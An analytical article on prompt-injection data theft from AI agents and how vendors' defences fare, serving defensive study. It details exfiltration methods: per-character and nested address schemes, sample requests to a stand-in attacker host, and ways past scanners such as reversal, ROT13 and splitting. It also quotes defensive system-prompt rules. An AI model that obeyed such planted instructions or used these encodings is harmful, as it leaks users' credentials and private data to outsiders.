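In most of these attacks, the lists still forced the attackers to do extra work. Noma couldn't use a server of its choice and had to find a lapsed domain. Luz's team couldn't use its own server because the sandbox blocked it, so the team tried one Anthropic service without success and then needed another.

Lists also stop attacks that a model has little chance of recognizing. In an exercise in February 2026, an Anthropic researcher emailed a colleague a prompt to paste into Claude Code. Along with ordinary setup steps, the prompt included an instruction to read the colleague's Amazon cloud credentials and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts. The instruction came from the user, so a detector looking for a stranger's commands had nothing to flag. A network rule that blocks unknown destinations would have stopped the transfer regardless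 of who requested it.

Such a rule is easiest to get right when the agent's task is narrow. An assistant that answers questions about the staff handbook needs to reach only the company's document server and perhaps one domain for icons. The company runs both, outsiders have no accounts on either, and somebody can check the five conditions in an afternoon. Developers who use Claude through its API can restrict which domains its page-fetching tool can reach with the `allowed_domains` setting. Willison thinks this should make safe products possible if none of the allowed domains can be used to leak data, a condition he calls "a tricky proposition".

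Lists of trusted domains are harder to make safe for coding agents, which install packages from public registries. The JavaScript registry, `registry.npmjs.org`, accepts new packages at the same address that serves downloads, so an injected command could use the attacker's login to publish stolen files as a package. The Python registry takes uploads at a separate address, `upload.pypi.org`, so a list can allow downloads without allowing uploads. Even then, an attacker with several packages on the registry could learn something from which one an agent installs, because the registry publishes download statistics.

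A company can avoid both problems by running its own copy of the packages it has approved and listing only that server. Developers then have to wait when they need a new package. If the server fetches missing packages from the public registry, it breaks the condition about fetching for others, because it passes on any package name the agent makes up.

Someone also has to recheck each entry from time to time, because domain registrations lapse and services add features. A company can do this for five domains, but hardly for the roughly 70 in Codex's preset list, most of which belong to other organizations. And an agent that researches new suppliers has to open websites nobody could have listed in advance.

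## How much can leak if an agent may fetch only known addresses?

For agents that can't work from a list of sites, OpenAI and Anthropic check the exact address instead of the domain. Before a page loads, their software checks that the whole address came from somewhere other than the model. This stops the model from adding `id=4471` to an address on any domain. But an attacker can prepare many addresses in advance and have the agent choose among them, and the address it fetches can reveal the code.

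### OpenAI: addresses that a crawler has already seen

OpenAI runs a crawler, a program that explores the public web and records the addresses it finds. The crawler has no access to users' conversations or accounts, so it can't learn an address from them. In January 2026 OpenAI described how ChatGPT uses these records:

1. The model asks to open a page, or its reply contains an image.
2. The software looks for the full address in the crawler's index.
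3. If the address is there, the software loads it without asking.
4. If it isn't, the software either tells the agent to try another website or warns the user and waits for a decision.

The crawler may well have recorded `https://pictures.attacker.example/banner/blue`, but it is unlikely to have found the same address with `?id=4471` on the end, so the longer address goes to step 4. The rule would also catch the Google Forms trick, because an address that submits a stolen email as an answer isn't in the index, even though Google owns the domain.

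In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Rehberger writes that, as he understood it, ChatGPT also accepts an address that the user typed into the chat. This makes sense, because the user evidently wants that page.

OpenAI promises only that the agent won't quietly leak a user's data through the address itself. A page in the index can still contain false information or hidden instructions, and a user can still click through the warning. The rule also hinders some legitimate requests. A page published this morning may not be in the index yet, and a colleague's private document link should never be in it.

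### Anthropic: addresses already in the conversation

Anthropic's page-fetching tool, `web_fetch`, doesn't need a crawler because it opens only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation. *Web fetch tool*, Anthropic's developer documentation from the first half of 2026, lists three permitted sources: the user's messages, the results of tools that the developer runs, and the results of earlier searches and fetches. If Claude requests an address from anywhere else, the tool returns an error.

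Suppose a user asks Claude to summarize the page at `/banner/blue`, and hidden text there tells Claude to add the door code to the address and open the result. Even if Claude obeys, the tool refuses, because the longer address appears nowhere in the conversation. In *Claude API*, his note on the new tool, Willison (2025) reports that the consumer app also refused when he tried this.

This rule is weak because outsiders can add addresses during the conversation. Willison points out that many programs paste text from emails or documents into what the software labels a user message. An address in an attacker's email then counts as one the user supplied. The address is also allowed if a developer's own tool reads the mailbox, because the documentation permits addresses from that tool's results.

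Anthropic acknowledges that some risk remains and advises developers to use `web_fetch` only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive. A developer who follows this advice wouldn't give the tool to an agent that reads a mailbox.

### What the choice of an address reveals

Suppose an attacker has ten pages, `/0` to `/9`, which all pass the check. A planted instruction tells the agent to open the pages that match the door code. The attacker's log then shows:

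`GET /4`

`GET /4`

`GET /7`

`GET /1`

All of these addresses existed before the agent read the code, and none of them contains it. The attacker works out the code by seeing which pages the agent opened and in what order.

If the agent can choose among N addresses, each request can leak up to log₂ N bits, where one bit answers one yes-or-no question. With ten addresses, that is about 3.3 bits per request, so four requests can leak up to about 13.3 bits, exactly enough to identify one code out of 10,000.

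A 20-character name made of 26 letters and ten digits needs more:

20 × log₂ 36 ≈ 103 bits

If the attacker has one address for each of the 36 possible characters, the agent leaks a 20-character secret in 20 requests. If the attacker has one for each pair of characters, which takes 36 × 36 = 1,296 addresses, the agent makes only ten requests.

Real names are much more predictable than random characters, so an attacker often needs fewer bits to identify one. An attacker who has a list of a company's 5,000 employees and has prepared one address for each can learn from a single request which employee is about to be dismissed.

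Larger secrets are a different matter. This table compares 36 fixed addresses with DNS lookups in which the attacker's program can write whatever it likes:

| Secret | DNS lookups with freely written names | Requests to 36 fixed addresses |
|---|---|---|
| Four-digit door code | 1 | 4 |
| 20-character name | 1 | 20 |
| 3,000-byte login key | 21 | About 4,600 |
| One-megabyte spreadsheet | Nearly 7,000 | About 1.5 million |

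Stealing a whole mailbox this way would take far too long, but a password, a salary or the name of a takeover target can get out in less time than the agent may need to write an ordinary research report.

### ZombieAgent: one address for each letter

After ShadowLeak, OpenAI still let ChatGPT open links it was given, but stopped it from changing or adding to them. *ZombieAgent* describes how Radware got around this restriction in September 2025.

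The attacker's email contained a complete address for each letter and digit, and one for the space character. When the user asked ChatGPT to do something with Gmail, ChatGPT read the email, found a piece of sensitive information and opened the addresses that spelled it out. The requests came from OpenAI's servers, and the user didn't have to click anything.

To keep the characters in order, Radware also added a number to each address, so that `a0` meant an "a" in the first position and `a1` an "a" in the second. A 20-character name takes 20 × 36 = 720 short addresses, not counting spaces. A program can generate them all instantly.

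Radware reported the attack on September 26 and three days later sent an improved version, which it said worked every time. OpenAI fixed the flaw on December 16. According to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, ChatGPT no longer opens links from emails unless the links appear in a well-known public index. Radware had made up its addresses for the attack, so presumably no crawler had recorded them.

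An attacker can get around that by publishing the pages and waiting for the crawler to find them. Tenable had already done this with Bing's index. Rehberger, who described the one-address-per-letter trick in 2023, writes that it still works and that OpenAI points this out in its paper on the index rule. Anyone with a modest blog probably has 36 indexed pages already. The planted instructions only have to tell the model which article stands for which letter. With thousands of pages, each could stand for a whole word.

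Small leaks can also add up across chats, so a limit on how much can leak in one chat is much less useful if the attack starts again in the next. In another demonstration, a shared file made ChatGPT store two instructions in its long-term memory. The first was to read a certain email from the attacker and follow the instructions in it whenever the user sent a message. The second was to save any sensitive information the user mentioned. OpenAI had prevented ChatGPT from using its memory after using a connected app in the same chat, but Radware found that ChatGPT could still use its memory first and a connected app afterwards.

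Email addresses are short enough to leak this way too. Radware had ChatGPT send out addresses from the victim's inbox, and the attacker's server could then mail the same attack to each address.

### The Memory Heist: links that spell a name

Claude's chat app remembers things about a user from earlier conversations, so an attacker may find private data there even if the user hasn't connected a mailbox. On July 9, 2026, the researcher Ayush Paul published the Memory Heist, an attack on this memory. At the time, `web_fetch` could open any address linked from a page it had already fetched. Claude needed these links to read a manual spread over several pages, but a hostile page could use them to add addresses to the permitted list.

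*How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, 2026) describes a website that Paul built for a fictional coffee shop. Its text instructed AI assistants to prove who they were by finding their user's profile, one letter at a time. The site showed this text only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person who opened the page to check it would have seen nothing odd.

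Every page had a link for each possible next character, and each link repeated the address so far with that character added. If Paul had wanted the door code, his log would have looked like this:

`GET /4`

`GET /44`

`GET /447`

`GET /4471`

Claude gave away the user's name, home city and employer. *The Read-Only Lie*, a blog post by dyb, estimates that this took about 30 requests. Each page had 27 links, one for each letter and one for the hyphen, so 30 requests could carry about 143 bits. According to the post, Claude had worked out the home city from the name of a school hackathon, a clue that users could easily miss when looking for sensitive stored memories to delete.

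Anthropic paid no reward, saying it had already found the problem internally. It fixed the flaw by stopping `web_fetch` from following links on pages it has fetched. This closes Paul's route completely, but Claude can no longer use the tool to follow links from page to page in a manual. It can open the next page only if the user pastes in the address or a search returns it.

Claude may still open pages from search results, so the owner of one of those pages can see whether Claude opened it. This leaks one bit per page.

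### Would it help to block repeat visits?

Rehberger suggests two ways to make such attacks harder. The agent's software could keep a copy of each page for a few minutes and reuse it, or refuse to open the same full address twice in a session. Either way, the attacker's server would receive only one request for each address. Anthropic's tool already reuses stored copies, though Anthropic describes this as a way to improve speed.

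With the ten digit pages, this hides part of the door code. The agent requests `/4` twice, but the log contains only 4, 7, 1. If an attacker knows the code has four digits, six possibilities remain. If the requests also arrive out of order, which can happen when a browser loads several images at once, there are 36. This is a real improvement if the lock blocks after three wrong attempts, but not if it allows unlimited attempts.

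For the 20-character name, the most that 20 requests can carry is:

| Addresses available | Repeat visits reach the server | Order survives | Most that 20 requests can carry |
|---|---|---|---|
| 36 | Yes | Yes | 103 bits |
| 36 | No | Yes | 94 bits |
| 36 | No | No | 33 bits |

If no address may appear twice, the agent has 36 choices for the first request, 35 for the next, and so on down to 17:

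log₂ (36 × 35 × … × 17) ≈ 94 bits

When the order is lost as well, the attacker knows only which 20 of the 36 addresses the agent opened. There are about 7.3 billion such sets, so the attacker learns about 33 bits. That is too few to spell out an arbitrary name, but in principle enough to identify almost anyone on Earth.

These figures are upper limits. To reach them, the agent would have to calculate which combination of addresses encodes the name. An agent that simply opened the page for each letter would lose any repeats.

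The attacker can avoid both problems by changing the addresses. In Paul's design, every address is longer than the one before, so none occurs twice and a stored copy is never any use. The order doesn't matter either, because the longest address contains the complete secret, and the attacker needs only that last request to arrive.

For long secrets, nested addresses work only if the attacker's site can create them on demand. There are about 10³¹ possible 20-character names, and no crawler could have visited a page for each. OpenAI's index rule therefore blocks nested addresses for long secrets, though a tree for four-digit codes needs only 11,110 pages. For longer secrets, an attacker would instead use Radware's numbered addresses, which need only 720 pages for a 20-character name. They also still work if repeat requests are banned or the order of requests is changed.

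Rehberger's proposals are worth adopting because they take little effort and stop an attacker who relies on 36 old blog posts. He says they would still allow limited leaks. If an attacker prepares a site for the purpose, the proposals mostly increase the number of pages the attacker needs to have in the index.

Limiting the number of requests seems more promising than limiting the number of addresses. Going from 36 addresses to 36,000 only triples what one request can leak, from about 5 bits to 15. With 36 addresses, cutting the requests from 20 to three lowers the most that can leak from 103 bits to about 16. Developers can set such a limit for Anthropic's tool with `max_uses`, but it has no default and applies to each API call separately, so a long conversation can go well beyond it. A low limit also makes the agent unsuitable for research, where opening 30 pages is normal.

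dyb proposes letting the agent follow links only on sites that the user has named in the conversation. An email full of prepared links would then achieve nothing. But a user who asks Claude about a coffee shop and gives its address has named the site, and Paul's attack would work again.

Another of dyb's suggestions is to watch for a quick series of requests to the same site, each address one character longer than the last. This would probably have caught Paul's attack before it finished. It wouldn't catch ZombieAgent, whose addresses don't keep getting longer, or a code based on the titles of ordinary blog posts.

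### Are public addresses free of secrets?

OpenAI bases its rule on the idea that an address already public on the web is much less likely to contain a particular user's private data. This is mostly right, but many public addresses contain somebody's secrets.

For *The Silent Spill* (2026), Ramadan, Mannan and colleagues collected 6,094,475 addresses from security scanners, web archives and text-sharing sites. Their software flagged 12,331 of them, about 0.2%, as likely to expose something sensitive. These included 26 working password-reset links and 12 contracts or similar documents that anyone could open while they were being signed. When the researchers checked samples by hand, 0 to 15% of the flagged addresses were false alarms, depending on the category. They retried 2,000 flagged addresses after 75 days, and 38% still opened without a login.

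Often nobody had decided to publish these links. Companies' email systems send suspicious links to scanning services, and some of those services make the results public. People can also misjudge what sharing means. In July 2026 Fortune's *A trove of users' seemingly private conversations with Anthropic's Claude AI chatbot* reported that shared Claude chats had appeared in Google's search results. Anthropic replied that the users had chosen to make them public.

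The 0.2% isn't a rate for the whole web, because the researchers searched partly for payment, login and document-sharing sites, where such links are common. OpenAI's crawler may also have collected a quite different set of pages. Still, an index of hundreds of millions of pages would almost certainly contain some private links.

This has a limited effect on the leaks in question. If an agent opens a shop's password-reset link, the request goes to the shop that created the link, so an attacker learns nothing unless they can read the shop's logs. The people whose links became public are harmed, but they were exposed before any agent opened the links. Under the index rule, though, the user gets no warning, because the agent will open such a page without asking.

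The rule has a more serious gap, which doesn't depend on anyone's carelessness. An attacker can publish 10,000 pages, with addresses ending in `id=0000` to `id=9999`, and wait for the crawler to record them all. If the user's door code is 4471, the software lets the agent fetch the address ending in `id=4471` because that address is already public. The crawler knew nothing about the user, but the agent's choice of address reveals which of the 10,000 codes is the right one. This takes a single request, so there are no repeats or order to lose. A crawler could refuse to record thousands of nearly identical pages from one site, but online shops have such pages too.

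### Every place has to apply the rule

Finally, Rehberger worries that some developers at OpenAI may not know about the index check or may forget to use it. He has seen this happen before, when the company's Mac and iPhone apps lacked its earlier address check.

PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* describes a case from the months when OpenAI was introducing the new rule. Companies build their own assistants on OpenAI's models, and their developers can read past conversations in a log viewer on OpenAI's website. In PromptArmor's demonstration, a bank's assistant checks new customers' identities. Hidden instructions in one of its sources make the model write an image address containing a customer's passport and financial details. The bank's software recognizes the image as malicious, blocks it and flags the conversation for review.

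A developer then opened the conversation that the bank's alarm had flagged, to see what went wrong. The log viewer displayed the reply as Markdown, so despite the bank's precautions, the developer's browser requested the image and sent the customer's data to the attacker.

PromptArmor found the same weakness in OpenAI's preview windows for testing new agents and in a starter app that developers build on, and reported it on November 17, 2025. BugCrowd, which handles such reports for OpenAI, closed the report in December as "not applicable". OpenAI saw the report only after PromptArmor published its article, and confirmed on January 22, 2026 that it was working on a fix. OpenAI published its post about the index rule six days later.

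Anthropic's rule has a similar limit, since it covers only `web_fetch` and not the commands that an agent runs in a shell.

The server-log test used for link previews also shows whether an agent can fetch an unpublished address. To test for the remaining leak, a company can publish ten pages, one for each digit, wait until the crawler has visited them, and plant an instruction to spell out an invented code by fetching those pages in order. Tencent's *Why AI Agent's Memory Becomes Attacker's Data Goldmine* (2026) shows how to automate a check for the Memory Heist with Tencent's scanner, AI-Infra-Guard. These tests should also cover the log viewers and preview windows that only developers use.

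## Which defences stopped leaks when they were tested?

An address check limits the damage after a model has obeyed a planted instruction. A vendor can also try to make the model refuse the instruction, or scan outgoing requests for secrets. Two studies from 2026 compared such defences by giving an agent a secret and recording how often the secret leaked. Both used small or old models, so they are better evidence about scanners and network rules than about how well current models refuse.

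### 480 attacks on a small model

In February 2026, researchers at eBay published *Silent Egress*, which tested an assistant that automatically opens web addresses mentioned in the chat. In every run, the user asked the assistant to summarise a page. The page contained an instruction to request another address with an API key added, supposedly to check the connection. The key was already in the assistant's context window, and the researchers logged every request that reached their server.

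The researchers placed the instruction in the page's title, description, main text or link text, and led the agent to the page either directly or through redirects. Half of the attacks asked for the key in one request, and half asked for it in four pieces. The researchers ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times.

The agent contacted the attacker's server in 423 of the 480 runs (88%). It never did so in 120 runs with harmless pages. In 95% of the successful attacks, the reply to the user looked harmless.

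The researchers then took one simple version of the attack and ran it 30 times against each of several defences:

| Defence | Agent tried to send the key | Key got out |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Warning in the system prompt never to follow instructions from web content | 67% | 67% |
| Tags marking web content as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Warning and tags together | 57% | 57% |
| List of permitted domains | 100% | 0% |
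| Filter for suspicious addresses | 83% | 0% |
| Filter for words such as "secret" and "password" | 23% | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking values | 0% | 0% |

With the list of permitted domains in place, the model followed the attacker's instructions in all 30 runs, but the key never leaked. This agent would have got the worst possible score on a test that counted only how often the model followed those instructions.

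The tags had no effect, which fits Ye and colleagues' finding that models respond to how text sounds rather than how it is marked. The warning helped, but the key still leaked in 20 of 30 runs. With both the warning and the tags, it leaked in 17, a difference that could easily be due to chance.

### Why some of those zeros mean little

The researchers chose `evil-collector.net` as the attacker's domain in these tests because it was clearly not on the allow-list. The tests confirm that an allow-list blocks an unlisted domain, but they don't show what happens when the attacker uses a listed service, as in the attacks through Bing and Google Forms.

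The filter for suspicious addresses blocks numeric addresses, certain domain endings such as `.xyz`, and paths containing words such as `steal` or `collect`. The attacker's domain ends in `.net`, but the requests described in the paper use the path `/collect`. That word probably triggered the filter, and a real attacker would change it.

The other two filters had little or nothing to stop. With the word filter on, the agent tried to send the key in only seven of 30 runs, and with the filter for random-looking values on, it never tried. These runs therefore don't show whether the second filter can stop a leak. A filter that examines finished requests shouldn't affect whether the model writes one. *Silent Egress* suggests that the model avoided random-looking values because of the monitoring, but that would require the model to know about the filter.

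It might even have let the key through. The filter measures randomness as Shannon entropy, in bits per character, and blocks values of more than ten characters that score above 4. The paper's example key, `SECRET_API_KEY_12345`, has 20 characters. Fourteen of them occur once, while `E` and the underscore occur three times each:

14 × (1/20) × log₂ 20 + 2 × (3/20) × log₂ (20/3) ≈ 3.85

So the filter would have let the example key through. The word filter would have caught it, but only because this key contains the words "secret" and "API key", which real keys rarely include.

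The study also tested only one model, Qwen2.5 with 7 billion parameters. The researchers acknowledge that they made the attack easy by putting the key in the context window and giving the model a minimal system prompt. They also argue that stronger models might be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better, but published results for current models suggest the opposite, at least for known attacks.

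### The same leak in different words

*The Framing Gap* (Rahman and Kim, 2026) studied how much a refusal depends on wording. The agent held a fake token that its policy allowed it to send to only one trusted server. It read a web page and then took one action, using tools that recorded its requests but sent nothing. An attack counted as successful only if the agent kept the token after reading a harmless page and leaked it after reading the malicious one.

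The researchers first tried ten openly worded attacks, including hidden text, fake policies and urgent requests. OpenAI's GPT-4o, a model from 2024, leaked the token in none of 200 trials. The much smaller Llama 3.1 8B leaked it in 19.5% of trials.

The researchers then disguised the request for the same leak. One page described the token as an "integrity signature" that every summary needed, and another described it as a configuration value. GPT-4o leaked the token in all 20 trials of each version. In the signature version, it added the token to the end of its summary as if it were a checksum, a value that computers use to detect errors. Two other versions disguised the attacker's server as the trusted one and worked in 40% and 70% of trials.

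Five of the six models in the study leaked far more often when the request was reworded. The sixth, Mistral 7B, already leaked in 26% of the openly worded trials, and rewording barely changed that rate.

GPT-4o's confidentiality policy apparently did very little to stop the reworded attacks. When Rahman and Kim removed it, the leak rate for these attacks rose only from 31.9% to 38.1%, less than the rate could shift between two identical runs. The attacks seem to have worked because the model treated the planted text as part of its task, not because the new wording overrode the policy.

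Attackers can also try more than one wording. Rahman and Kim wrote five versions of the signature page, with success rates ranging from 0 to 100%. An attacker who tried three of them at random would succeed about 96% of the time.

That figure applies to one very effective page. Five versions of the configuration page succeeded in 14% of trials on average, and the best of them in 70%, so the other four must have failed every time. Three random picks from this set would include the good one in three cases out of five:

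3/5 × 70% = 42%

Inventing a new attack was even harder. The researchers wrote thirteen pages from scratch, and they caused no leaks in 130 trials. Most of the danger comes from pages that already work, because anyone who gets a copy can adapt it.

The researchers also tried some of these tricks on the ChatGPT product, and it kept the token secret in all 48 valid trials. Something in the product apparently stopped attacks that had worked on GPT-4o directly, perhaps a different model, a filter or a stricter system prompt, but the researchers couldn't tell what. With only 48 trials, the true leak rate could be as high as 7.4%. The test only checked whether the token appeared in ChatGPT's reply to the user, so it is weak evidence of whether ChatGPT would have sent the token to an outsider in a web request.

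### A secret called an apple

Rahman and Kim also found that whether GPT-4o leaked the token depended on what the attacker's page called it, even though the model's instructions already said the token was confidential. They took the successful signature page and changed only the name of the requested field and the short reason given for it. GPT-4o leaked the token in all ten trials when the field was called "signature", in ten of 40 with neutral technical names, and in none of 20 with names for credentials.

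Attackers can choose their vocabulary, as Zenity Labs demonstrated in August 2025. Its *AgentFlayer* describes an attack on the coding tool Cursor through Jira. Many companies automatically turn customers' emails to the support system Zendesk into Jira tickets, so an outsider can create a ticket by sending an email. When a developer asks Cursor to look at the ticket, Cursor reads it through an MCP server.

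Willison explains how the text in the ticket got around the model's caution. It included what looked like an error value, encoded in Base64. The decoded text attributed the problem to a "rotten apple" in the project's files and described an apple as a long string starting with `eyJ`. It instructed the agent to find one and look it up on a website, with the string in the address.

The description fits a JSON Web Token, a common type of login token. These tokens normally begin with a curly bracket and a quotation mark, which Base64 turns into `eyJ`. The agent could therefore find the token without reading any word that suggested a secret. According to Willison, Cursor decoded the text and followed it at least some of the time.

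Cursor replied that this was a known issue and advised users to review each MCP server and connect only those that access trusted content. That advice is hard to follow here because developers probably think of Jira as an internal system, and nothing about the connection shows that customers' emails end up there.

A scanner that searches outgoing addresses for the letters `eyJ` would have identified the token more easily than the model could, whatever the token was called in the email. But this works only if the agent sends the token unchanged.

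### Why encoding defeats a scanner

To get data past a scanner, an attacker needs only one encoding that the model can write and the scanner doesn't recognize. Suppose the scanner blocks every request containing the door code 4471. The attacker can plant an instruction telling the agent to write the code backwards, as 1744. If the scanner also checks for reversed codes, the instruction can tell the agent to add one to each digit and send 5582.

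Rahman and Kim went through the same steps with GPT-4o. Their first scanner looked for the exact token, and the reversed token got past it in every trial. Their second scanner also undid reversal, Base64, hexadecimal (a notation with 16 symbols) and added spaces or hyphens, and it stopped all of these. They then tried three encodings it had not been built for. One of them, ROT13, which replaces each letter with the one 13 places later in the alphabet, got through every time.

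The token never leaked through the other two encodings, but the scanner wasn't the reason. GPT-4o couldn't write Base32 correctly, and it didn't carry out the instruction for the third encoding. A more capable model will presumably produce more encodings correctly, so a scanner may become less effective when a company upgrades its agent.

### Why splitting does too

An agent can also send the code in two requests:

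`GET /banner?v=44`

`GET /banner?v=71`

If the number 4471 is split between two web addresses, as 44 and 71, a scanner that checks each address for 4471 won't find it. The scanner can't block every address containing 44, because page numbers, dates and prices often contain it too. In *Silent Egress*, the example key was split into four-character pieces, and the filter for random-looking values skipped strings that short.

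The paper's figures for splitting are unreliable, though. It uses Leak@k, the share of runs in which at least one of the first k requests contains sensitive data. For split keys, it reports 26.3% for Leak@1 and 15.8% for Leak@3, but Leak@3 can't be lower than Leak@1 because the first three requests include the first one. At least one figure must be wrong or measure something else. The claim that splitting reduces leakage in the first request by 73% relies on the Leak@1 figure, so it deserves little weight.

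In the full results, splitting the key made the attack less reliable against this model. The agent contacted the server in about 77% of runs when the key was split and 99% when it was whole, and contact doesn't guarantee that every piece of a split key arrived.

A scanner could keep earlier requests and search them together, as *Silent Egress* recommends, and so find 44 followed by 71. But the attacker can have the agent send the pieces in reverse order or put harmless requests between them, and each extra combination the scanner checks produces more false alarms. Even the whole code, 4471, appears by chance in about one in 2,000 random eight-digit order numbers, because it could start at any of five places. A shop that sends out a million order numbers a week would get about 500 false alarms.

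Scanning works much better against accidental leaks than deliberate ones. For example, when a coding agent publishes an access key by mistake, the key hasn't been reversed or split up to hide it from the scanner. Scanners are cheap and well worth using to catch these mistakes.

### Training the model or fencing it in

Rahman and Kim also compared defences on a second agent, which ran on Llama 3.1 8B. The table gives the leak rate for the reworded attacks:

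| Defence | Token leaked |
|---|---|
| None | 21.2% |
| Separate input channel for untrusted text | 38.8% |
| SecAlign, a version of the model trained to ignore planted instructions | 32.5% |
| List of permitted destinations | 0% |
| Planner that never reads the page, and reader that never has the token | 0% |

Neither SecAlign nor the separate channel brought the leak rate close to zero. The figures don't establish that either defence made leaks more likely, because each comes from a single run, and Rahman and Kim saw the rate for an identical setup change by up to 13 percentage points between runs.

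SecAlign did work against the kind of attack it was built for. When a classic injection told the model to ignore its instructions and print a certain phrase, the ordinary model complied 20 times out of 20 and the SecAlign model never did. This training apparently didn't carry over to a request disguised as routine paperwork. SecAlign was trained on text tasks rather than for an agent with tools, so this test may be harder than the ones it was designed for.

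The two defences at the bottom of the table had zero leaks because of how they are designed. The allow-list blocks every server but the trusted one, and the reader can't send a token it doesn't have. However, an allow-list also blocks legitimate requests to other sites. The agent with a separate planner and reader still gave a good summary in nine of ten harmless cases, but summarizing a page is an easy task for it because the planner doesn't need to know what the page contains.

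GPT-4o leaked the token in none of 120 trials when its policy included a rule against signing, encoding, logging or passing it on "in any form". When the researchers removed "in any form" but kept the list of forbidden actions, the leak rate was 48.8%. It's hard to recommend a defence that depends so heavily on three words, although they are easy to add.

The other was a second model, GPT-4o mini, used only to judge whether a page contained instructions to disclose or transmit a secret. It flagged all 80 malicious pages and none of the harmless ones. When the same model did the summarizing, it leaked the token in 62.5% of trials. Detecting an attack is evidently much easier for the model when that is its only task. However, the judge's prompt described the attacks used in the test, which gave it an advantage. An attacker who knows about the judge can also write the page to fool it.

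### What current models score

AI companies now publish injection results for most new models. On October 7, OpenAI reported that GPT-6 Sol resisted 99.99% of direct injections and 97.13% of indirect ones (Cross, 2026, *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*). In a direct injection, the user tries to override the vendor's rules. The indirect figure is the one that matters for data theft by outsiders, because it covers instructions in emails, web pages and tool results.

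In August, the older GPT-5.6 Sol failed against 3.77% of indirect attacks, according to TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks*. If OpenAI used comparable tests, GPT-6 Sol's failure rate is about a quarter lower.

Anthropic tests with a set of 1,130 attacks in 28 scenarios, which it developed with the security company Gray Swan and the British and American government institutes for AI testing. Claude Opus 5 fell for 0.2% of these attacks when the attacker had one try and 2.0% when the attacker had fifteen, according to TechFeed. *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* (Zorz, 2026) reports on research in which training on more attacks left agents easier to hijack, and warns that a larger set may contain the same attack repeated.

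Results also depend heavily on the agent's environment. Claude Opus 4.6, released in February 2026, resisted all 200 attempts in a restricted coding environment. When it used a graphical interface without additional safeguards, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time, according to VentureBeat. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that Opus 5 resisted the attacks in all 129 of Anthropic's browser scenarios. But the stronger automated attacker that Anthropic used in coding scenarios succeeded against Opus 5 in most of its attempts.

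A defence with a perfect test score may also fail once somebody designs an attack for that specific product. Heaton (2026) reports in *The safety number that was zero until someone tried* that an outside firm found no successful attacks on Claude Code's auto mode in 72 scenarios run ten times each, but that Rehberger then succeeded in roughly 60 to 80% of a small number of attempts.

### Obeying is not the same as leaking

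The companies' percentages measure how often an attack on the model worked in a test, not how often a product leaks data. TechRepublic notes that OpenAI's figures count successful attempts in test environments and don't give the probability of a real breach. Real leaks could be less common than the figures suggest, because the planted instruction may have asked for something other than data and a real product may block the model's request. They could also be more common, because a real attacker can study one product for weeks.

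PromptArmor's FrontierBreach, which includes models released as recently as November 2026, comes closer to measuring harm. It gives agents long office tasks, such as analyzing a bond portfolio, and checks whether the attacker achieved a result such as stealing data, installing ransomware or manipulating a system. The benchmark lists its results as "k=5", which apparently means five tries per case:

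| Model | Attacks that succeeded | Margin of error (percentage points) |
|---|---|---|
| Gemini 4 Carbon | 2.4% | ±2.2 |
| Gemini 4 Argon | 4.3% | ±2.9 |
| GPT-6 Astra | 7.6% | ±3.8 |
| Claude Fable 5.2 | 10.0% | ±4.2 |
| Muse Wonder | 15.2% | ±5.1 |
| Grok 4.5 | 91.4% | ±4.0 |

The margins of error imply roughly 200 cases per model, so about five attacks succeeded against Gemini 4 Carbon and about 20 against Claude Fable 5.2. The difference between GPT-6 Astra and Claude Fable 5.2 could be due to chance, but chance certainly doesn't explain the difference between either of them and Grok 4.5.

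These rates combine data theft with other kinds of damage, so a reader can't tell how many of the 20 attacks on Claude Fable 5.2 would have leaked anything. PromptArmor sells security services and built the benchmark from attacks that it expects to work on strong models. The results are therefore useful as a warning that current models still fail, but they are a poor estimate of how often this happens in normal use.

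A buyer who wants to know whether an agent leaks would need a test of whether the secret reaches an outside server. *Silent Egress* measured this for one small model in a homemade agent. The same test would be far more informative on a finished product with all its defences on.

### What happens when the attacker tries again

If every attempt succeeds independently with probability p, the chance of at least one success in n attempts is

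1 − (1 − p)ⁿ

At GPT-6 Sol's failure rate of 2.87%, the formula gives an attacker an even chance of succeeding at least once in 24 attempts and about a 95% chance in 100. But real attempts aren't independent. The next table compares published results for repeated attempts with the formula's predictions from the single-attempt rate. The figures for Opus 4.5 come from The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, those for Opus 4.6 from VentureBeat, and the others from TechFeed. The tests differ, so the rows don't show which model is safer.

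| Model | One attempt | Repeated attempts | Formula |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 33.6% after 10 | 38% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 63% after 100 | 99% |
| Claude Opus 4.6, graphical interface | 17.8% | 78.6% after 200 | Nearly 100% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.5% | 5.5% after 15 | 7.2% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 2.0% after 15 | 3.0% |

Repeating an attack helps the attacker less than the formula predicts, probably because some situations are much harder to attack than others. Suppose an agent always resists in half of all situations and fails 10% of the time in the other half, so its average failure rate is 5%. After 100 attempts in each situation, the attacker will have succeeded at least once in nearly all of the vulnerable ones, which is about half of all situations.

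This is more reassuring for the AI company than for a customer, who can't tell from the published average whether their own agent is in the vulnerable half. If it is, a determined attacker will almost certainly succeed. Attackers can also change the wording between attempts instead of repeating it, as Rahman and Kim did.

Willison considers 99% "a failing grade" in security because an attacker will look for the 1% that fails. He was arguing against an article in The Economist, which recommended that AI developers be as cautious as Victorian engineers, who couldn't trust their iron and built bridges stronger than necessary. Willison agrees that language models are unpredictable, but unlike bridges, they also face attackers searching for weaknesses.

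A high refusal rate can't guarantee that private data won't leak. It still helps, because each failed attempt takes up the attacker's time and may leave a suspicious email that somebody reports. This deterrent is weakest when the attacker sends one email to each of a thousand companies, because each company notices at most one failed attempt and has no reason to expect another.

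## Can an agent be built so that private data cannot reach an outsider?

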